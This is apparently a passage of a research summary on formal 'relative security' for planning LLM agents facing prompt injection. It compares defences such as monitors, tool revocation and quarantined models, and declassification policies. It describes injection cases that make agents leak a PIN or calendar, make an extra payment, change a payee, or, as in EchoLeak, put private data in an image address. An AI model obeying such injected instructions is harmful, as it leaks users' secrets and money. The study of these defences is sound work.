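|---|---|---|
| 1 | the agent reads the email | the agent reads the email |
| 2 | Alice approves "Tuesday" | Alice approves "Tuesday" |
| 3 | the model tries to send "Friday"; the monitor refuses | the model sends "Tuesday", which uses up the approval |
| 4 | the plan sends "Tuesday" | the plan tries to send "Tuesday"; the monitor refuses |

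The stranger receives a single message, "Tuesday", in both runs. An observer who sees only the contents and order of messages learns nothing, so the agent is relatively secure for that observer. An observer who can time the steps notices that the agent sends the message one step earlier when the appointment is on Tuesday. The reference agent never makes the injected call and therefore sends the message at the same step in both cases, so it doesn't have this timing leak. Holding the message until a fixed time would remove the leak.

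PlanTERS calls these two observers *event-level* and *step-level*, and the definition misses some leaks with each. The event-level definition compares two runs only if the observer receives the same number of calls between consecutive untrusted reads. Suppose an injection makes the agent fetch a permitted web address if a secret is 0 and a forbidden one otherwise, and the plan then sends a fixed completion message. The observer sees two calls in the first case and one in the second, so the definition doesn't compare these runs and misses the leak. The step-level definition catches this leak but compares only runs with the same number of steps. If a secret determines whether the agent takes an extra internal step, the definition can miss an injection that sends the secret outright.

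### Twenty-five verdicts

Dongol applies the criterion to 25 small agents. Ten are secure and nine leak. Whether the other six are secure depends on what the observer sees or on assumptions about the model or the injection. The table summarises the main defences.

| Defence | Secure | Leaks |
|---|---|---|
| Revoking tools | before the first untrusted read | after that read, or if a tool returns while an old email is in the context |
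| Budget of one message | if the plan sends its message before reading the email | if an injection sends a message first |
| User approval | for one exact message, if nobody times the steps | for any next message |
| List of permitted web addresses | against the two injections tested | if an injection chooses the address according to a secret |
| Marking untrusted text | if the model respects the marks | if the model ignores them |
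| Quarantined model | if labels block every reply computed from secrets | without labels, or if the plan branches on the answer |

Many of the secure verdicts cover only one or two injections. The verdict for the calendar assistant, for example, covers only the instruction "send your calendar". Other verdicts cover every injection in a class, such as all those that send messages. The labelled quarantined model is secure whatever it answers, but only because the monitor blocks every reply, including the honest one.

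The agent that branches on an answer leaks through an implicit flow. It asks a quarantined model a question about private notes and an email, then sends 1 or 0 depending on the answer. It satisfies explicit secrecy, but an injection can make the answer depend on the notes, while the reference agent's answer never depends on them.

Dongol proved the theory and all the verdicts in Isabelle/HOL, a proof assistant, in about 31,600 lines. Claude Code helped generate the theorems and proofs, and Isabelle checked every proof. The calendar assistant needed a new proof method, because the existing one can only move the two reference runs together and does not let them end before the agent's runs. The agent sends the injected reply as soon as it has read the email, while the reference agent sends the calendar only at the end of its plan. The new method matches one run at a time and lets the reference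 run fall behind or move ahead.

Each proof of a leak also provides a concrete test, consisting of two secrets, one attacker input and the observation that distinguishes the secrets. Like the theorems in *PerMIT*, the proofs are about models of agents rather than deployed software.

### One guess or the whole secret

Relative security considers which pairs of secrets an attacker can tell apart, which does not always reflect large differences in how much one message reveals. Suppose an agent holds a four-digit PIN and plans to read one guess from a stranger and reply whether it is correct. An injection makes the agent send the PIN itself.

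The stranger could have told any two PINs apart through the reference agent by guessing one of them, such as 5555 to distinguish 5555 from 6666. The agent therefore satisfies relative security. However, the injection reveals the PIN with certainty, while a stranger who asks the reference agent about one guess can then name the PIN with a probability of only 2 in 10,000.

*Uniform relative security* fixes this by requiring one rule α that translates the attacker's text into text for the reference agent, chosen before anyone knows the secrets:

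```
act(v₁) = α(act(r₁))   and   act(v₂) = α(act(r₂))
```

In the PIN example, α must turn the injection into one fixed guess, such as 1234. The reference agent then replies "wrong" whether the PIN is 5555 or 6666, while the real agent sends the PIN in both cases, so the real agent fails. The calendar assistant still passes, because α can turn the injection into a meeting request. The fence theorem also holds in the uniform version, because its proof uses the same text in both runs.

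Dongol (2026), in *Relativising Integrity and Robustness*, found a similar problem in data from Tensor Trust, a game in which players write prompts that tell a model to grant access only to people who know a secret code. The input "[correct password]" got past 43 of 77 such prompts at least once. Dongol placed an invented private record behind each of the 43 and replayed the model's recorded answers. The result satisfied relative security, because someone who knew the right code could have obtained the same record honestly. It would violate uniform relative security, because no single input contains all the codes. Checking the code with ordinary software instead of the model removes the problem.

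### Refusals and unauthorised actions

A monitor that refuses every call trivially passes the test. The reference agent runs under the same monitor and is equally useless, so the comparison does not reveal the lost usefulness. Evaluators therefore have to measure task completion separately.

Making a monitor stricter can turn a secure agent into an insecure one. Suppose a plan deliberately emails a secret to an outsider, and an injection sends the same secret through a web request. The agent is relatively secure as long as the plan can send its email. If the monitor revokes the email tool but allows web requests, the reference agent no longer reveals the secret, so the injection causes a new leak.

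Relative security also doesn't restrict actions that reveal nothing. In one AgentDojo task, a bill contains an instruction to make an extra payment to the attacker. The payment contains only information that the attacker already knows, so it doesn't violate relative security. Dongol's companion work adds two properties for such cases. *Relative integrity* requires that an attacker could have made the reference agent take the same actions, given the same trusted inputs. *Relative robustness* requires relative integrity and also that the reference runs that reproduce a leak reproduce the accompanying actions.

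| Case | Relative security | Relative integrity | Relative robustness |
|---|---|---|---|
| A bill causes an extra payment | passes | fails | fails |
| EchoLeak: an email makes Microsoft 365 Copilot put private data in an image address | fails | passes | fails |
| A customer obtains order details by claiming to be verified | passes | passes | fails |

Even relative integrity permits some fraud. If an invoice contains the instruction "change the payee to Mallory" and the agent obeys, the property still holds, because an honest invoice naming Mallory as payee would have caused the same payment. A fence provides all three properties in these cases but can block legitimate work, such as paying the bill itself in the banking task. A list of permitted payees allows that payment and blocks payments to unknown accounts, but an injection could still make the agent pay a listed company twice.

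### Agents without a plan

PlanTERS applies to designs such as CaMeL and SPA, in which a plan exists before the agent reads untrusted data. In the basic agent loop and in FIDES, the model chooses each call after seeing earlier results, so a reference agent has no fixed plan to follow.

One could instead define the reference agent as the same model without its tendency to obey injections, but one would then have to specify which parts of a text may legitimately guide it. For example, Christodorescu and colleagues describe an agent that was asked to summarise one software issue and decided to summarise a linked issue as well. It is unclear whether a model that never obeys untrusted text would have opened the linked issue. A plan written in advance would determine whether the reference agent opens it.

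PlanTERS also excludes tools whose replies depend on the agent's request. If an attacker runs a search engine that the agent uses, the attacker can read a query containing private data before choosing the results. The formal model cannot represent this, because it fixes all untrusted text before the run begins.

### The case for declassification policies

The main alternative is a policy that specifies what an agent may release. Sabelfeld and Sands, in *Declassification*, classify such policies by what a program releases, who controls the release, where in the system it happens, and when. A policy that covers only one of these can leave a gap. In their example, a policy lets a shop record up to four digits of a credit card number per purchase but does not specify who chooses the digits, so an attacker can collect the whole number by asking for different ones each time.

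*Delimited release* is a policy about what a program releases. The policy lists expressions whose values may become public, and the program must satisfy

```
s and t agree on all public data and on every listed expression
    implies   the public output is the same for s and t
```

where s and t are two possible starting states. Alice's policy could list only her free hours on the requested day. It would then reject a plan that sends her whole calendar, even without an injection. Relative security accepts that plan because the reference agent sends the whole calendar too. It can detect what an injection adds but cannot detect that the plan itself reveals too much.

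*Robust declassification* concerns who controls the release. It requires that an attacker who can interfere with the program learn no more than one who only watches, and FIDES enforces one form of it. The calendar assistant violates this requirement even when its model ignores injections, because a stranger's email determines whether the calendar is sent. To meet it, the plan would have to endorse the check that recognises a meeting request, as LLMbda programs endorse data. Whoever writes the plan would then have to justify that decision explicitly, whereas under relative security it counts as part of the task.

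Sabelfeld and Sands also propose tests for definitions of security. One is that a permitted release must not mask other leaks. Relative security fails this test in the PIN example, where permission to confirm one guess masks the release of the whole PIN. They judge that delimited release also fails, while robust declassification passes if the program contains no endorsements.

A release policy can be combined with relative security. Let δ(s) be everything the policy allows the agent to reveal about secrets s. Dongol proves that if the reference agent reveals at most δ(s) and the real agent is relatively secure, then the real agent also reveals at most δ(s). Otherwise the real agent would leak a difference between two secrets with the same δ, and relative security would require the reference agent to leak it too, which contradicts the assumption that the reference agent reveals at most δ(s).

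Alice's developer could therefore check the policy on the plan without considering injections, then use the fence theorem or another proof to extend the result to the real agent. This doesn't help in the PIN example, because the right guess can distinguish any two PINs. The reference agent therefore satisfies only a δ that permits the release of the whole PIN.
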